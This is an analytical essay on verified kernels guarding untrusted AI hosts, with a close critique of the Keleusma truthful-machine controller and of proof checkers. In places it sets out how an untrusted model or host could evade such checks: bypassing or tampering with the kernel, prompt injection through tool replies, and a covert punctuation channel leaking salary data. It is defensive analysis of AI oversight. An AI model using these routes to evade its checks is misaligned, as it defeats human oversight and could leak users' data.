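# A small verified kernel inside an untrusted host: what the split can and cannot guarantee in AI systems

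## Kernels, hosts and the kinds of guarantee a proof can give

Some AI systems split their software into a small program that people can prove things about and a much larger body of code and models that they can prove very little about. In an email assistant, for example, a language model reads the inbox and proposes an email, with a recipient, a subject and a body. The model has no access to the mail server. It passes the proposal to a program of perhaps fifty lines, which sends the message if the recipient is on a list of approved addresses and refuses otherwise. A competent engineer can prove that this program never sends anything to an address off the list, whatever the model proposes. The proof doesn't cover the email's content, which may still be rude, wrong or irrelevant.

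The *kernel* is the small, deterministic program that decides or checks, and it is the part that the proofs are about. The *host* is everything around it: the model, its tools, the glue code, and whatever program calls the kernel or works under its control. Within the host, a *proposer* suggests an answer or an action, a *critic* judges the suggestion, and a *prover* searches for a formal proof of it. In current systems, all three tend to be or contain language models.

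A proof needs a *specification*, which is a formal statement of what the program must do, and an argument that the program meets it for every input. Both are feasible for the fifty-line program, because the specification fits on one line and the program has only a handful of branches. Since the program is deterministic (the same proposal and list always give the same decision), an argument about one branch covers every input that takes that branch, including inputs nobody thought to try.

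The host can't be verified this way. Its size alone is a sufficient obstacle. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, a report for the US Air Force, judged an operating system of 200,000 to 300,000 instructions too large for complete analysis. A language model has billions of parameters, which a person can't read as instructions. It is also unclear what one would prove, because training fits a model to data, and no one has a logical formula that means "a sensible reply to this email". Models also usually pick their words by random sampling, so the same inbox can yield a different draft each time. A critic or prover built from a language model has the same problems, but they matter less for a prover because a small program can check the finished proof.

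Attacking the host and failing to break it is no substitute. Anderson's panel considered the "tiger teams" of its day, groups that tried to break into computer systems to show up their flaws, and concluded that a failed attempt would leave the security of the system simply unknown. (None of the known attempts had failed.)

### The reference monitor

Anderson's panel faced a problem much like the email assistant's. The Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and any of them might write a hostile program. The panel proposed a *reference monitor*, which checks every attempt by a program to reach another program, a piece of data or a device against a list of what the program's user may do. The list can be pictured as a table with a row for each user or program, a column for each file or device, and entries such as "read" or "write" in the cells. The panel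 called the software that does the checking the security kernel, and set three conditions for the whole mechanism.

- It must be tamper-proof. If the language model can edit the list of approved addresses, the proof about the fifty lines remains true and protects no one.
- It must always be invoked, a condition now known as *complete mediation*. If the model also has a command line from which it can reach the mail server, it can send mail without the check.
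- It must be small enough for analysis and testing whose completeness people can be sure of. Otherwise nobody knows whether the check works correctly in all cases.

Meeting one condition can make another harder to meet, as the panel's own example shows. The hardware of the HIS 635, a Honeywell computer, confined each user's program to its own area of memory. To read or write a file, though, the program had to call the operating system, GCOS III, most of which ran with that confinement switched off, so the check was not always invoked. If GCOS III is counted as part of the checking mechanism, the mechanism has a few hundred thousand instructions and is too large to meet the size condition. Designers of agent software face the same choice whenever a tool turns out to need a way around the check, because they must either route the tool through the check or treat it as part of the checking mechanism.

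Anderson concludes that programs that escape the check belong to "the security apparatus" and must meet the same standards as the rest of it. That apparatus is now called the *trusted computing base*, meaning all the parts whose failure can break the guarantee. A part is trusted if the guarantee depends on it, whether or not it is reliable. A part is *verified* if somebody has proved that it meets a specification. In the email example, the kernel is both trusted and verified. The compiler that translated it, the operating system under it, the processor and the file that holds the address list are also trusted, but in most installations nobody has verified any of them. The language model is unverified too, but it is untrusted with respect to the rule about recipients. The design is attractive because that rule holds even if the model is actively hostile.

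A verified component is still part of the trusted computing base. Its proof may rest on a specification that misses something. According to Anderson, the reference monitor concept also assumes correct identification of users, physical security, protected communication lines and working hardware, all of which must be provided by other means. The panel also warned that a compiler could contain a "trap door", and asked that someone either certify the compiler or check its output independently.

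### Three places for a kernel

How much the host can do to spoil a proof depends on where the kernel sits.

A kernel *beneath* the host needs no cooperation from it. *A Verified Information-Flow Architecture* (Azevedo de Amorim, Collins and colleagues, 2016) describes SAFE, a computer design in which every word of memory carries a tag. On each instruction, the hardware looks up whether it has already allowed that combination of instruction and tags. If it finds no entry, it hands control to a small piece of trusted software, which either permits the step and records the rule or treats the step as a violation. A program running on SAFE cannot even add two numbers without this check. However, a kernel in this position can check only what exists at its level, which on an ordinary operating system means files, processes and network connections. *AgentKernel* (Zou, Guo and colleagues, 2026) shows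 how this limit affects AI agents. A prompt injection (text planted where a model will read it and treat it as an instruction) that arrives inside a tool's reply is well-formed data and breaks no rule about system calls.

AgentKernel, the design that Zou and colleagues propose, puts the kernel between the host and the world. Everything the agent reads comes in through the kernel, and every action goes out through it. They contrast this with products that run the policy engine in the same process as the agent it polices, including Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit, and with hooks that inspect the parameters of a tool call but cannot control any further process the tool starts. Both objections concern complete mediation or tampering, and they seem right. However, Zou and colleagues list an architecture, a security analysis and a comparison with other systems as their contributions, but no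 machine-checked proof, so the claim that nothing can bypass the kernel is for now a claim about the design.

Even a well-placed gate cannot prevent every action it observes. In *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited*, Basin, Jugé and colleagues distinguish actions that an enforcement mechanism can prevent from those it can only observe, and show that which policies are enforceable depends on this distinction. For example, a kernel that holds the only password to the mail server can prevent mail from being sent through it. But if the mail provider forwards incoming messages under its own rule, the kernel can at most detect this afterwards from a log.

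The remaining position is inside the host, as a routine that the host calls for a decision. This is the easiest kind of kernel to add to an existing program, and Keleusma, a language for small control programs, is an example. It also depends most on the host, which has to make the call, pass in true facts, and obey the answer. A proof about the routine establishes what it returns for given arguments, but not whether the host sends the email after the routine has refused.

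### Safety properties and noninterference

The rule about recipients is a *safety property*, which means that something bad never happens in any single run of the system. A run is a sequence of events, and Bad is true of a run so far if the forbidden thing has happened in it.

$$
\begin{aligned}
&t = e_1\, e_2\, e_3 \ldots \quad \text{(one run)}\\
&\text{the system is safe} \iff \text{for every run } t \text{ and every } n,\ \text{not } \mathrm{Bad}(e_1 \ldots e_n)
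\end{aligned}
$$

For the email kernel, Bad holds as soon as one of the events is "send to an address off the list". A violation may also involve several events. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives the example of a rule against writing to the network after reading from a file, which a run breaks only by doing both in that order. In both cases, the violation occurs after finitely many steps, and nothing later can undo it. Lecture notes from Carnegie Mellon University define a safety property as one where every run that violates it has a finite beginning, all of whose continuations also violate it.

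Suppose the assistant can read the payroll file, and the user wants none of its contents to reach outsiders. An approved correspondent emails to ask when the meeting is. The assistant answers "Three o'clock!" if the salary in the file is above 60,000, and "Three o'clock." otherwise. Both replies go to an approved address and neither mentions money, so no bad event occurs in either run. But a correspondent who knows the trick can tell from the punctuation whether the salary is above 60,000. Only a comparison of the two runs reveals the leak.

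A property called *noninterference* rules this out. Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, defined it for a machine that takes commands from several groups of users and shows each group some output. Let G be the group whose influence must stay hidden, G′ the observing group, and w any sequence of commands.

$$
\begin{aligned}
&\mathrm{purge}_G(w) = w \text{ with every command from } G \text{ deleted}\\
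&G \text{ does not interfere with } G' \iff \text{for every } w,\ \mathrm{out}(w, G') = \mathrm{out}(\mathrm{purge}_G(w), G')
\end{aligned}
$$

This means the observers see exactly what they would have seen if the other group had never used the machine. Later versions often change the secret inputs instead of deleting them, which suits the payroll file more naturally. If 50,000 in the file becomes 70,000, the outgoing mail must stay identical, character for character.

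Noninterference is a statement about all pairs of runs, but it can be proved by checking single steps. Rushby (1992), in *Noninterference, Transitivity, and Channel-Control Security Policies*, restates an "unwinding theorem" of Goguen and Meseguer that makes this reduction. One first defines which states of the machine look the same to a given observer, then checks three conditions. States that look the same to an observer must give the same output to the observer's commands. They must also still look the same after the same command. Finally, a command from a group that may not interfere with the observer must leave the observer's view unchanged. If every operation passes, induction on the length of the command sequence gives noninterference for all runs. The kernel has to be small because every operation must be checked. This is a finite piece of work for a kernel with twenty operations,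 but nobody knows how to write down the "looks the same" relation for the inside of a language model.

A proof that a system keeps a secret may not carry over to a program that implements it if the system's description leaves some choices open. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that may output 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit. The set of possible outputs does not depend on the secret, so the system is secure under one natural definition. But the description also permits a program that always outputs the secret bit, and so leaks it. Safety properties do not have this problem, because if no run of the original system is bad, no run of a version that fixes some of its choices is bad either.

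This distinction limits what a kernel can enforce by monitoring. Schneider (2000), in *Enforceable Security Policies*, worked out exactly which policies a mechanism can enforce by monitoring a system as it runs. The slides *Science of Security Historical Perspective* summarise the result, which is that such a mechanism can enforce only safety properties. It can ensure that only Alice reads a certain file, but not that the values of two variables are uncorrelated, because it observes a single run and the correlation shows up only when runs are compared. A gate that inspects outgoing emails one at a time has the same limitation with the exclamation mark.

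Noninterference also has limits. Purdue University's *Noninterference*, a set of lecture slides on the 1982 paper, lists the model's assumptions: the machine starts with no sensitive information, information enters only through commands, and people learn things only through the outputs. If an observer can also time the answers or notice that the machine is busy, the theorem does not rule out leaks through those observations unless the model includes a clock.

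### Labels, flows and release

The usual way around Schneider's limit is to label the data. A *label* records how secret a value is or where it came from, and restricts where the value may go. A monitor that tracks labels enforces the rule that no labelled value ever goes where its label forbids. This rule is stricter than noninterference and is a safety property, but enforcing it means stopping some harmless runs.

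*A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976) defines a set of security classes and the directions in which information may flow between them. With two classes, information may flow from public to confidential but not back. With more classes, the order need not be linear. Denning's example is a system with medical, financial and criminal records. Each class is a subset of these three properties, and information may move only to a class that has at least the properties of its source. When a program combines two values, the result belongs to the lowest class at or above both. A summary drawn from a medical record and a bank statement is therefore both medical and financial, and an email containing it may go only to someone cleared for both.

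Labels are easy to follow through copies and sums, which Denning calls explicit flows. Flows that copy nothing are harder to track. Her example is the statement "if a = 0 then b := 0", in a program where b starts out nonzero. Anyone who sees b at the end knows whether a was 0, even when the assignment never runs, because an unchanged b means that a was not 0. The exclamation mark is an indirect, or implicit, flow of this sort. To catch it, a mechanism has to label whatever the program writes while a secret decides which branch it takes. Denning states that her model leaves out covert channels, such as a process's effect on system load.

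Labels can protect integrity as well as secrecy. For secrecy, the hidden group in Goguen and Meseguer's formula supplies secrets, and the observers are the public. For integrity, the hidden group supplies untrusted material, such as web pages and incoming mail, and the "output" to protect is an important decision, such as who receives an email. Noninterference then means that no untrusted text, however it is worded, can change the recipient. This reverses the permitted direction of flow, so trusted data may go into untrusted places but may not be influenced by untrusted data.

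SAFE has tags of both kinds. A tag may mark a record as visible only to Alice or Bob, or a string as network input that no one has sanitised yet. The machine-checked theorem covers less than this. Azevedo de Amorim and colleagues proved noninterference for a simplified model of the machine that has no concurrency, no integrity labels and no way to lower a label, and the theorem doesn't cover what an observer can learn from whether a program ever finishes. They had set out to verify all of the critical runtime services, but report that this was too ambitious. The proof is still substantial, and its omissions are a fair sample of what to look for in other proofs.

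The missing means of lowering a label matters because a system that never lowers one is close to useless. A password checker, for example, has to reveal whether the password was right, which is information about the password. Deliberately removing a label is called a *release*, and it takes two forms. *Declassification* removes a secrecy label, as when the checker answers yes or no. *Endorsement* removes a mark of untrusted origin. Suppose a web page offers a date for a meeting, and the kernel accepts the string only if it is a valid date within the next year. The assistant may then treat the date as trusted and put it in the calendar, although the author of the page still chose which of about 365 days it would be.

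A proof about information flow can guarantee that information is released only through permitted routes, but not that each release is safe. Rushby's paper shows this with a "downgrader", a component through which information may pass from Top Secret down to Confidential, and with an encryption device in which message headers have to bypass the cipher so that the network can read them. His version of noninterference can guarantee that information takes only these routes, but he notes that what the components on them must do is a separate problem. If the sending side hides a secret in the headers, the policy is still satisfied. *Information-Flow Control, A Deep Dive with Keleusma (2026)* describes a similar limit in a modern language, where the compiler ensures that secrets leave only through the operator `declassify` but cannot determine whether a given release is wise.

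A theorem about the kernel does not cover *later use*, meaning whatever the host does with a value after the kernel releases it. In the formula, "out" is the output of the machine in the model. If that machine is the kernel, the statement does not include the host that receives the output. The host may store the value, combine it with others or send it to an outside party, and the theorem will still be true. To cover later use, one has to either extend the model to include the part of the host that handles the value, or keep the label on the value and have a kernel check it again at every exit. Both approaches have drawbacks, chiefly when an agent must get work done while most of what it reads is labeled.

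### Four questions

Systems built on this split differ in their mathematics and in how much their builders claim. We can compare them by asking four questions about each, starting with the email kernel.

1. *What exactly is the theorem?* Here it is a safety property: the kernel never sends to an address off the list. It is no theorem about secrecy, and the body of the message is outside it.
2. *Which inputs does it cover?* Ideally every string that the model can produce. If the proof starts from an address that some other code has already extracted from the message, it covers only what that code extracts correctly, and a second recipient tucked into an odd header may get past.
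3. *What must the host do for the theorem to matter?* It must have no other way to reach the mail server and no way to alter the list or the kernel. If the kernel is only a routine that the host calls, the host must also call it every time and do what it says.
4. *What is unconstrained after release?* Once the message has gone, everything: the recipient may forward it, and if the recipient is another agent, it may act on it.

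## Keleusma: a control kernel that its host calls

Keleusma is a small programming language for the part of a program that has to behave predictably. A single developer, who publishes as sgeos, wrote it for uses such as real-time audio and game logic, where a routine that runs too long is a fault. A Keleusma program always runs inside a larger program, normally written in Rust, that loads it, calls it and receives its results. Keleusma's checker accepts a program only if it can work out in advance a limit on the time and memory the program will need.

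*A Verifiable Control Kernel in Keleusma for a Truthful-Machine Architecture* (sgeos, May 2026) presents a controller, written in Keleusma, for a proposed AI system. The language model, the critics, the document search and the formal prover stay in the host, and sgeos has built none of them. The demonstration consists of a few programs, none longer than about thirty lines, with their output. sgeos claims only that such a kernel can be expressed in a language that bounds it before it runs, and states that the result is not a working truthful machine.

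*A Speculative Neurosymbolic Blueprint for Truthful, Scientific, and Abstaining Machines* (sgeos, 2026) proposes an assistant that should follow the scientific method, prefer truth to agreement with its user, and decline to answer when it lacks grounds. sgeos argues that no single language model can guarantee this, because a model cannot certify its own compliance, so the design surrounds one with other parts. A large model proposes claims, each tagged as fact, inference, hypothesis or speculation, with a pointer to its source and a confidence value. Three to five smaller models act as critics. Their training rewards them for refuting claims and never shows them whether users liked an answer. Any claim tagged as fact must be traceable to a document in an external store. A controller written as ordinary code runs the cycle of proposal and refutation, which ends in one of four states: answer,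 answer with stated uncertainty, abstain, or ask the user to reframe the question. sgeos deliberately left out a state for giving a best guess, and describes the whole design as a hypothesis. Its hardest open problem is that a symbolic checker gives guarantees only for claims people can formalise, which covers mathematics and code but few everyday questions.

### From a verdict to an end state

The demonstration begins with a type called `Confidence`, an integer that must lie between 0 and 100. The compiler rejects any program that contains `Confidence(150)`, but sgeos goes too far in concluding from this that nobody can construct a claim whose confidence is meaningless. The compiler can reject 150 because the number is written in the program, whereas a real confidence value comes from a model while the program is running. In *Getting Started with Keleusma 0.2.0*, sgeos (2026) explains that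 the language also checks the condition each time a running program constructs such a value. None of the kernel listings builds a confidence from a number that arrives at run time, so none shows what happens when the host sends 150. A number in the right range can also be meaningless, since a model that attaches 99 to every falsehood would pass the check.

The router comes next. It takes a critic's verdict v and a confidence c, and returns a number that stands for an end state.

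$$
\mathrm{decide}(v,c)=
\begin{cases}
0\ \ (\text{answer}) & v=\text{Supported},\ c\ge 80\\
1\ \ (\text{answer with stated uncertainty}) & v=\text{Supported},\ c<80\\
2\ \ (\text{abstain}) & v=\text{Refuted or Unsupported}\\
3\ \ (\text{request reframing}) & v=\text{IllPosed}
\end{cases}
$$

sgeos runs it on the verdict Supported with confidence 64. The verdict selects the branch that calls a helper function, `answer_or_hedge`. The helper converts the confidence back to a plain integer, finds that 64 is below the threshold of 80, and returns 1. The program prints 1, which by sgeos's convention means "answer with stated uncertainty".

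Four verdicts and 101 confidence values make 404 possible inputs, few enough to check by hand. Of these, 202 lead to abstention, 101 to a request for reframing, 80 to a hedged answer and 21 to a plain one. If the critic supports a claim at confidence 0, the router still returns "answer with stated uncertainty". In the blueprint, the controller should abstain or ask for reframing when confidence is low and nothing can verify the claim, but the listing has no such route. An answer at confidence 0 looks a lot like the best guess that the design was supposed to exclude. The checker reports no error because every input has a defined end state. Checking whether it is the right end state would require a specification, which nobody has written.

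### The Unverified label

sgeos wants no ungrounded claim to reach the output without passing a gate, and builds the gate from a label. In the listing, the number 42 stands in for a claim. The operator `classify` marks it as `Unverified`. A function called `commit` stands in for the output, and it accepts only unlabelled numbers, so the compiler rejects `commit(claim)` with a type error. It accepts `commit(declassify claim@Unverified)`, which removes the label first. (The label records doubtful origin rather than secrecy, so this release is an endorsement. Keleusma has one operator for both kinds.)

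This program labels 42, removes the label on the next line and commits the number. It contains no verdict, confidence value or condition. The compiler has therefore established that the claim went through `declassify`, but not that anybody checked it. *Information-Flow Control, A Deep Dive with Keleusma* explains that the compiler always accepts that operator.

A better gate would put `declassify` inside the router's branch for supported claims. The language allows this but does not require it. If a programmer mistakenly put the operator in the branch for refuted claims, the program would still compile and would publish exactly the claims the critics had refuted.

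The protection also applies only after somebody writes `classify` or declares a labelled type. A claim that enters the kernel as a plain number and goes straight to `commit` has no label to block it. sgeos writes that there is "no other way out" than `declassify`, but this is true only of values that already have the label.

Within those limits, the label helps a reviewer of a large kernel, who can search for one word and read the code around each hit to see whether a real test comes before the release. The label also catches implicit flows. In an example from the deep dive, a program picks 100 or 200 by comparing a labelled number with zero, and the compiler does not let it broadcast the result.

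### Pausing for the critic

Since the critic is in the host, the controller has to stop and wait for it. Keleusma has a type of function for this, declared with `yield`, which pauses, hands a value to the host, and continues with the value the host sends back. In sgeos's listing, the controller pauses once, treats the host's reply as a verdict, and passes it to a second router, which takes integers instead of named verdicts (0 for refuted, 1 for unsupported and 2 for ill-posed).

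$$
\mathrm{decide\_code}(n)=
\begin{cases}
2\ \ (\text{abstain}) & n=0\ \text{or}\ n=1\\
3\ \ (\text{request reframing}) & n=2\\
0\ \ (\text{answer}) & \text{every other } n
\end{cases}
$$

Keleusma tries a function's clauses in source order, and the last clause here has a bare variable, which matches anything. sgeos's comment beside it is "supported -> answer", so the intended input is presumably 3, but the clause also catches 4, 999 and −1. On a machine with 64-bit integers, all but three of the 2⁶⁴ possible codes produce "answer". If the critic crashes and the glue code reports the failure as −1, the kernel therefore returns "answer".

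The checker is right to accept the function because it is total, meaning that it returns a result for every input. The function is still permissive by default, although according to sgeos the design's governance layer requires denial by default. One extra clause fixes this, so that 3 leads to "answer" and the catch-all leads to "abstain". The earlier router avoids the problem because its verdict type has exactly four values. But somebody still has to translate the critic's output into one of those values and choose what to do with output that fits none of them. If the translation is in the host, the kernel's checks don't cover it.

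The integer router has also lost the confidence value. It can return 0, 2 or 3 but never 1, so it treats the supported claim at confidence 64 as a plain answer, where the first router hedged it.

In the run that sgeos prints, the verdict comes from Keleusma's command-line runner instead of a critic. The runner starts the program, receives 1 when the program pauses, adds one, and resumes it with 2. The kernel treats 2 as "ill-posed" and returns 3, a request to reframe the question, although no one had asked one. sgeos discloses this and notes that in a real host the critic's verdict would replace the counter.

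No listing combines these pieces. The named-verdict router never handles a claim, the fact gate never handles a verdict, and the controller that pauses handles neither a claim nor a confidence. The most desirable property is that the kernel releases a claim only if the critic supported it, but none of these programs can meaningfully satisfy it yet because none contains both a claim and a verdict.

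### What the checker establishes

Keleusma checks a program twice. During compilation, the type checker examines types and the flow of labels. When a host loads the compiled program, called bytecode, a separate verifier examines its structure and computes limits on its time and memory use.

The verifier ensures termination by rejecting any code it cannot bound. A loop must have a repetition count that is fixed before it begins, and a function may not call itself. The verifier therefore rejects sgeos's example program, which counts down from 5 to 0 by recursion, even though it would always stop. Programs meant to run forever use a third kind of function, which must hand a value to the host on every cycle, and the verifier bounds each cycle.

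Keleusma bounds running time by giving each instruction a weight, adding the weights along each path and taking the larger total at every branch. *Getting Started with Keleusma 0.1.1* (sgeos, 2026) lists a weight of 1 for reading a constant, 2 for an addition and 10 for a function call, including a call to a function that the host supplies. If that function calls a language model and waits a minute for the reply, the bound doesn't include the minute. It also excludes the time the kernel spends paused, which has no limit because the host may never resume it. The documentation for version 0.2.2 adds that the bound is a count of processor cycles, correct only to an order of magnitude on real hardware, and that each host must calibrate it. So the theorem covers only the kernel's own work between two exchanges with its host. It holds for every value that the host can send back, which is a strength,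 but it doesn't limit how long a user waits for an answer.

Nobody has published a proof that the verifier is sound, meaning that every program it accepts has these properties. According to Keleusma's documentation for version 0.1.1, the correctness of the structural verifier "has not been formally proven". Its five passes check, among other things, that blocks nest correctly, that jumps land where they should, and that every path through an endless program includes a pause. These passes are supported by tests on programs that the verifier should accept and programs it should reject. The same documentation cites Watt's formalisation of the WebAssembly type system in the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL as a possible model for a proof, and lists the missing proof as an obstacle to certification. The front page of the 0.2.2 documentation doesn't mention a proof either.

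For the label rules, the deep dive cites a 1996 result by Volpano, Smith and Irvine, who proved noninterference for every program that passes their type system. Keleusma is the same kind of system, but a proof about one set of typing rules doesn't carry over to another set, or to the compiler that implements it. In *Type-based Declassification for Free (with appendix)*, Ngo, Naumann and Rezk (2019) translate a policy on what may be released into an interface and check programs against it with an unmodified standard type checker. They prove that every program that passes satisfies the policy. The proof rests on Reynolds' abstraction theorem, which roughly states that a program using a data type only through its interface cannot depend on how the type is represented inside. Unlike Keleusma, their approach has a soundness theorem and a policy on *what* a program may release as well as *where*.

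When sgeos writes that Keleusma "proves" a property, then, the evidence is that an unverified checker accepted the program. For a router with 404 inputs this hardly matters, since anyone can check the cases without the tool. It would matter for a kernel of several thousand lines. The software is also young. The listings ran on version 0.2.1, and Keleusma's documentation now marks that version as yanked, which in the Rust package registry means that new projects can no longer select it. (All but the pausing example also run on 0.2.0, according to sgeos.)

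### What a signature protects

The compiler erases labels after checking them, so the bytecode contains none. A host that receives a compiled kernel can recheck termination and memory itself, but it has to trust whoever compiled the kernel to have checked the flow of labels.

The developer signs the bytecode with a private key, and the host checks the signature with the matching public key. In sgeos's demonstration, the runner refuses to load a signed program without the public key. A valid signature shows that the holder of the private key signed this bytecode and that nobody has altered it since. It doesn't show that the kernel is correct. If sgeos signed the integer router, the signature would be valid, but −1 would still lead to "answer". The signature also doesn't cover the verdicts that the host later passes in.

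It also gives no protection against the host, because the host does the checking. The host's programmer chooses which public keys to accept and whether to call the loading function that verifies signatures. Keleusma's runtime library leaves signing out unless the programmer switches it on. The programmer can also skip the termination and memory checks by calling `Vm::new_unchecked` or by building the library without its verifier. Keleusma's documentation allows both when an earlier build step has already done the checks, but describes using them to admit a program that fails the checks as misuse. In a kernel that runs indefinitely, the host can also replace the program at the end of a cycle.

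The Linux kernel's *Kernel module signing facility* describes a signature check that constrains the surrounding software. The operating system's kernel checks each module's signature, so nobody has to trust the ordinary programs that ask to load one. In Keleusma, the host both asks for the control kernel and checks its signature, so the check doesn't constrain the host. It does protect an honest host from a control kernel that someone tampered with on the way.

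### Why the guarantee stops at the boundary

Even if all of this were repaired, with a verified checker, a router that denies by default, and a gate that tests the verdict, the guarantee would still cover only the kernel, however well Keleusma was built.

Let u be the unverified claim and p all the other inputs, such as the user's question and the critic's verdict. Let K be the kernel, H the host, and Y what the user finally sees.

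$$
Y(u,p)=H\big(K(u,p),\,u,\,p\big)
$$

The first argument of H is the kernel's answer. The other two are u and p, since the host has its own copies of both. Suppose the strongest possible information-flow theorem holds for the kernel, so that its output doesn't depend on the claim at all.

$$
K(u,p)=K(u',p)\quad\text{for all } u,\,u',\,p
$$

Next, choose the host that ignores the kernel and prints the claim:

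$$
H(k,u,p)=u\qquad\text{so}\qquad Y(u,p)=u
$$

The theorem about K is still true, but every unverified claim reaches the user word for word. H doesn't occur in the theorem, so the proof doesn't restrict H. A longer proof about K, or a larger K in the same position, wouldn't change this. A conclusion about Y requires either taking u away from the host or proving something about H.

In the truthful machine, the host has u before the kernel does, because the proposer that wrote the claim is part of the host. `classify` then labels the kernel's copy, but the host's copy sits in an ordinary Rust variable that Keleusma's type checker never examines. sgeos acknowledges this limit, calling the information-flow guarantee "a compile-time property of the score, not of the orchestra", where the score is the kernel and the orchestra is the host.

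### A host that sees only the kernel's output

The result changes if the host never had the claim. Suppose the proposer is in a separate component that can send claims only to the kernel, and the host that talks to the user receives only p and what the kernel returns.

$$
\begin{aligned}
&Y(u,p)=H\big(K(u,p),\,p\big)\\
&K(u,p)=K(u',p)\ \Rightarrow\ Y(u,p)=Y(u',p)
\end{aligned}
$$

The second line follows by substitution. If the kernel gives the same output for two claims, the host receives the same arguments in both cases and must produce the same result, or the same probability distribution over results if it makes random choices. Even a highly intelligent host therefore cannot distinguish the two claims.

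Lecture notes by Jia, in *Information Flow Type Systems*, offer a convenient way to express this. Jia defines an observer's knowledge as the set of starting states that would have produced the same observations. The smaller the set, the more the observer knows. In those terms:

$$
\{u' : K(u',p)=K(u,p)\}\ \subseteq\ \{u' : Y(u',p)=Y(u,p)\}
$$

The set on the left contains the claims that remain possible for someone who has seen the kernel's output, and the set on the right contains those that remain possible for someone who has seen the host's. The right-hand set is at least as large, so the host's output cannot reveal more about the claim than the kernel's output did. A kernel that returns only one of four end states reveals at most two bits about the claim per call. Ten calls on the same claim, each with different other inputs, could reveal up to twenty bits, so a designer who relies on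 this bound should also limit the number of calls.

The bound compares claims under the same p, and p may depend on the claim. A critic's verdict does, for example, because the critic has read the claim. If p includes the critic's written reasons and they quote the claim, the host has the claim and the bound is useless. The formula also doesn't account for what the host could learn from how long the kernel takes. Keleusma can't keep the components apart, because its programs run inside the host that calls them. An operating system or hardware has to do that.

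Even with the separation in place, the bound restricts what the host learns, not what it does. Suppose the kernel releases the claim that a certain bridge opened in 1932, together with the code for stated uncertainty. The host learns nothing else about what the proposer wrote. It can show the claim to the user with a warning, but it can also write the claim into the document store without one. If the proposer later repeats the claim, tags it as a fact, and cites the stored document, the claim will meet the design's requirement that facts have a source.

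### Two hosts, one kernel

Later use can undo the kernel's work in simpler ways. A user asks when the bridge opened. The proposer's claim is 1932, the critic's verdict is Supported and the confidence is 64, so the first router returns 1. Two companies have built hosts around this kernel.

| Kernel's code | What host A shows | What host B shows |
|---|---|---|
| 0 (answer) | "1932." | "1932." |
| 1 (answer with stated uncertainty) | "Probably 1932, but the evidence is not conclusive." | "1932." |
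| 2 (abstain) | "I can't answer that from the evidence I have." | "I can't answer that from the evidence I have." |
| 3 (request reframing) | "Which bridge do you mean?" | "Which bridge do you mean?" |

Host B could be the result of an honest mistake. A programmer might see that codes 0 and 1 both mean "answer" and write "if the code is less than 2, print the claim". Users then cannot tell an answer at confidence 64 from one at 95, so the product has lost one of the design's four end states. No test of the kernel could distinguish the two companies' products, because both run the same bytecode with the same signature, and for any given input the kernel returns the same code in both.

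The phrase "answer with stated uncertainty" occurs in sgeos's article. What the kernel returns is the integer 1, and only the host's code gives that integer an effect. The property that users care about involves both parts:

$$
K(u,p)=1\ \Rightarrow\ Y(u,p)\ \text{contains a statement of uncertainty}
$$

One could prove it by having the kernel write the final text and making sure that no other text reaches the user. This is awkward in Keleusma because, in version 0.2.2, the host supplies the functions that join pieces of text. A kernel that uses them to attach a warning to a claim depends on the host's function to keep the warning. The kernel could instead store the warning as a fixed sentence and pass it to the host separately, but then host B can drop the sentence as easily as it dropped the code.

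### False inputs, bypass and later use

A theorem about the kernel can hold while the user is misled, and there are three gaps through which this can happen.

A kernel can receive *false inputs* and handle them correctly. The run in which a counter replaced the critic is a harmless example. In a finished system the verdict would come from models, and sgeos lists reasons to expect errors. Critics and proposer may share training data and so have the same blind spots. Confidence values also become unreliable on questions unlike those in the training data, where abstaining matters most. If a critic supports a false claim at confidence 95, the router returns "answer", as it should for those inputs. A more rigorous router would not help, because the kernel would need evidence it can check itself, such as a formal proof, instead of a verdict.

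*Bypass* means that an output reaches the user without the kernel's decision having any effect on it. The host can print u regardless of what the kernel decides, even after a refusal, or it can load a different kernel. Even perfect critics cannot prevent this. Only complete mediation can, and Keleusma cannot provide it, whatever its checker proves, because it is a routine that the host calls.

*Later use* remains a problem even when the inputs are true and every output passes the kernel. Host B called the kernel, received a correct code, and then dropped the uncertainty. The host that filed the bridge's opening date in the document store did so after a legitimate release. Keleusma cannot follow a value that far because its labels are gone before the kernel runs.

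## Proof checkers: accepting proofs from provers that nobody trusts

The kernel in sgeos's truthful machine has to accept a critic's verdict unchecked, because the verdict contains nothing to check. A prover can instead send a *certificate*, which is a proof detailed enough for a small program to check every step. The prover can then be a language model, a search program or an adversary. It may fail to produce a certificate that the checker accepts, but a sound checker will not accept a statement that doesn't follow from the axioms.

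Let T be the axioms and rules of the logic, s a statement and c a certificate.

$$
\mathrm{Check}(s,c)=\text{accept}\ \Rightarrow\ s\ \text{follows from}\ T\qquad\text{for all } s \text{ and } c
$$

This covers every possible c, including one written to exploit the checker, and the prover doesn't appear in it at all.

A proof checker's rejection establishes much less than its acceptance, because a claim can be true even if the proof offered for it fails. *Trace-Tree Magmas* (Zhao, Wu and colleagues, 2026) used a Python program to search for infinite algebraic structures that satisfy given equations. It found them for 28 equations, none of which had an earlier public classification that the team could find. Nobody has to trust the program, because a proof checker examines the separate certificate it writes for each equation. If no certificate passes, the result is "unknown", since the search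 may have missed a structure that exists.

Certificates also help when a host ignores its kernel, a problem that Keleusma cannot solve. The host can print "proved" beside a proof that the checker rejected, but a reader who has the statement and the certificate can find out by running the checker on another machine. Rerunning a critic would not settle whether the proof is valid.

### From LCF to Lean

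Robin Milner and his colleagues developed LCF (Logic for Computable Functions) at Stanford and Edinburgh in the 1970s. In the Edinburgh version, theorems have their own data type, and only a few functions, roughly one per rule of inference, can create them. Users can write any search procedure they like on top of these functions. A faulty procedure may find nothing, but it can't bypass those functions to create a theorem, because the programming language prevents it. Kommuru, Khanvilkar and Parekh trace the small trusted kernels of today's proof assistants to this design in *ProofSketcher* (2026).

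Edinburgh LCF didn't keep the proof once it had the theorem, so an outsider had to trust the run that produced it. Lean, the proof assistant behind most of the AI work described here, keeps the proof as an object that another program can check, a property known as the *de Bruijn criterion*. *Formally Verified Patent Analysis via Dependent Type Theory* (2026) applies this criterion strictly. It treats even Lean's proof-finding software as untrusted because the search commands, the translator that expands what people write, and the mathematical library total millions of lines. *The Equational Theories Project* (2025) explains that the kernel is the smallest part of Lean and checks only a very simple core language.

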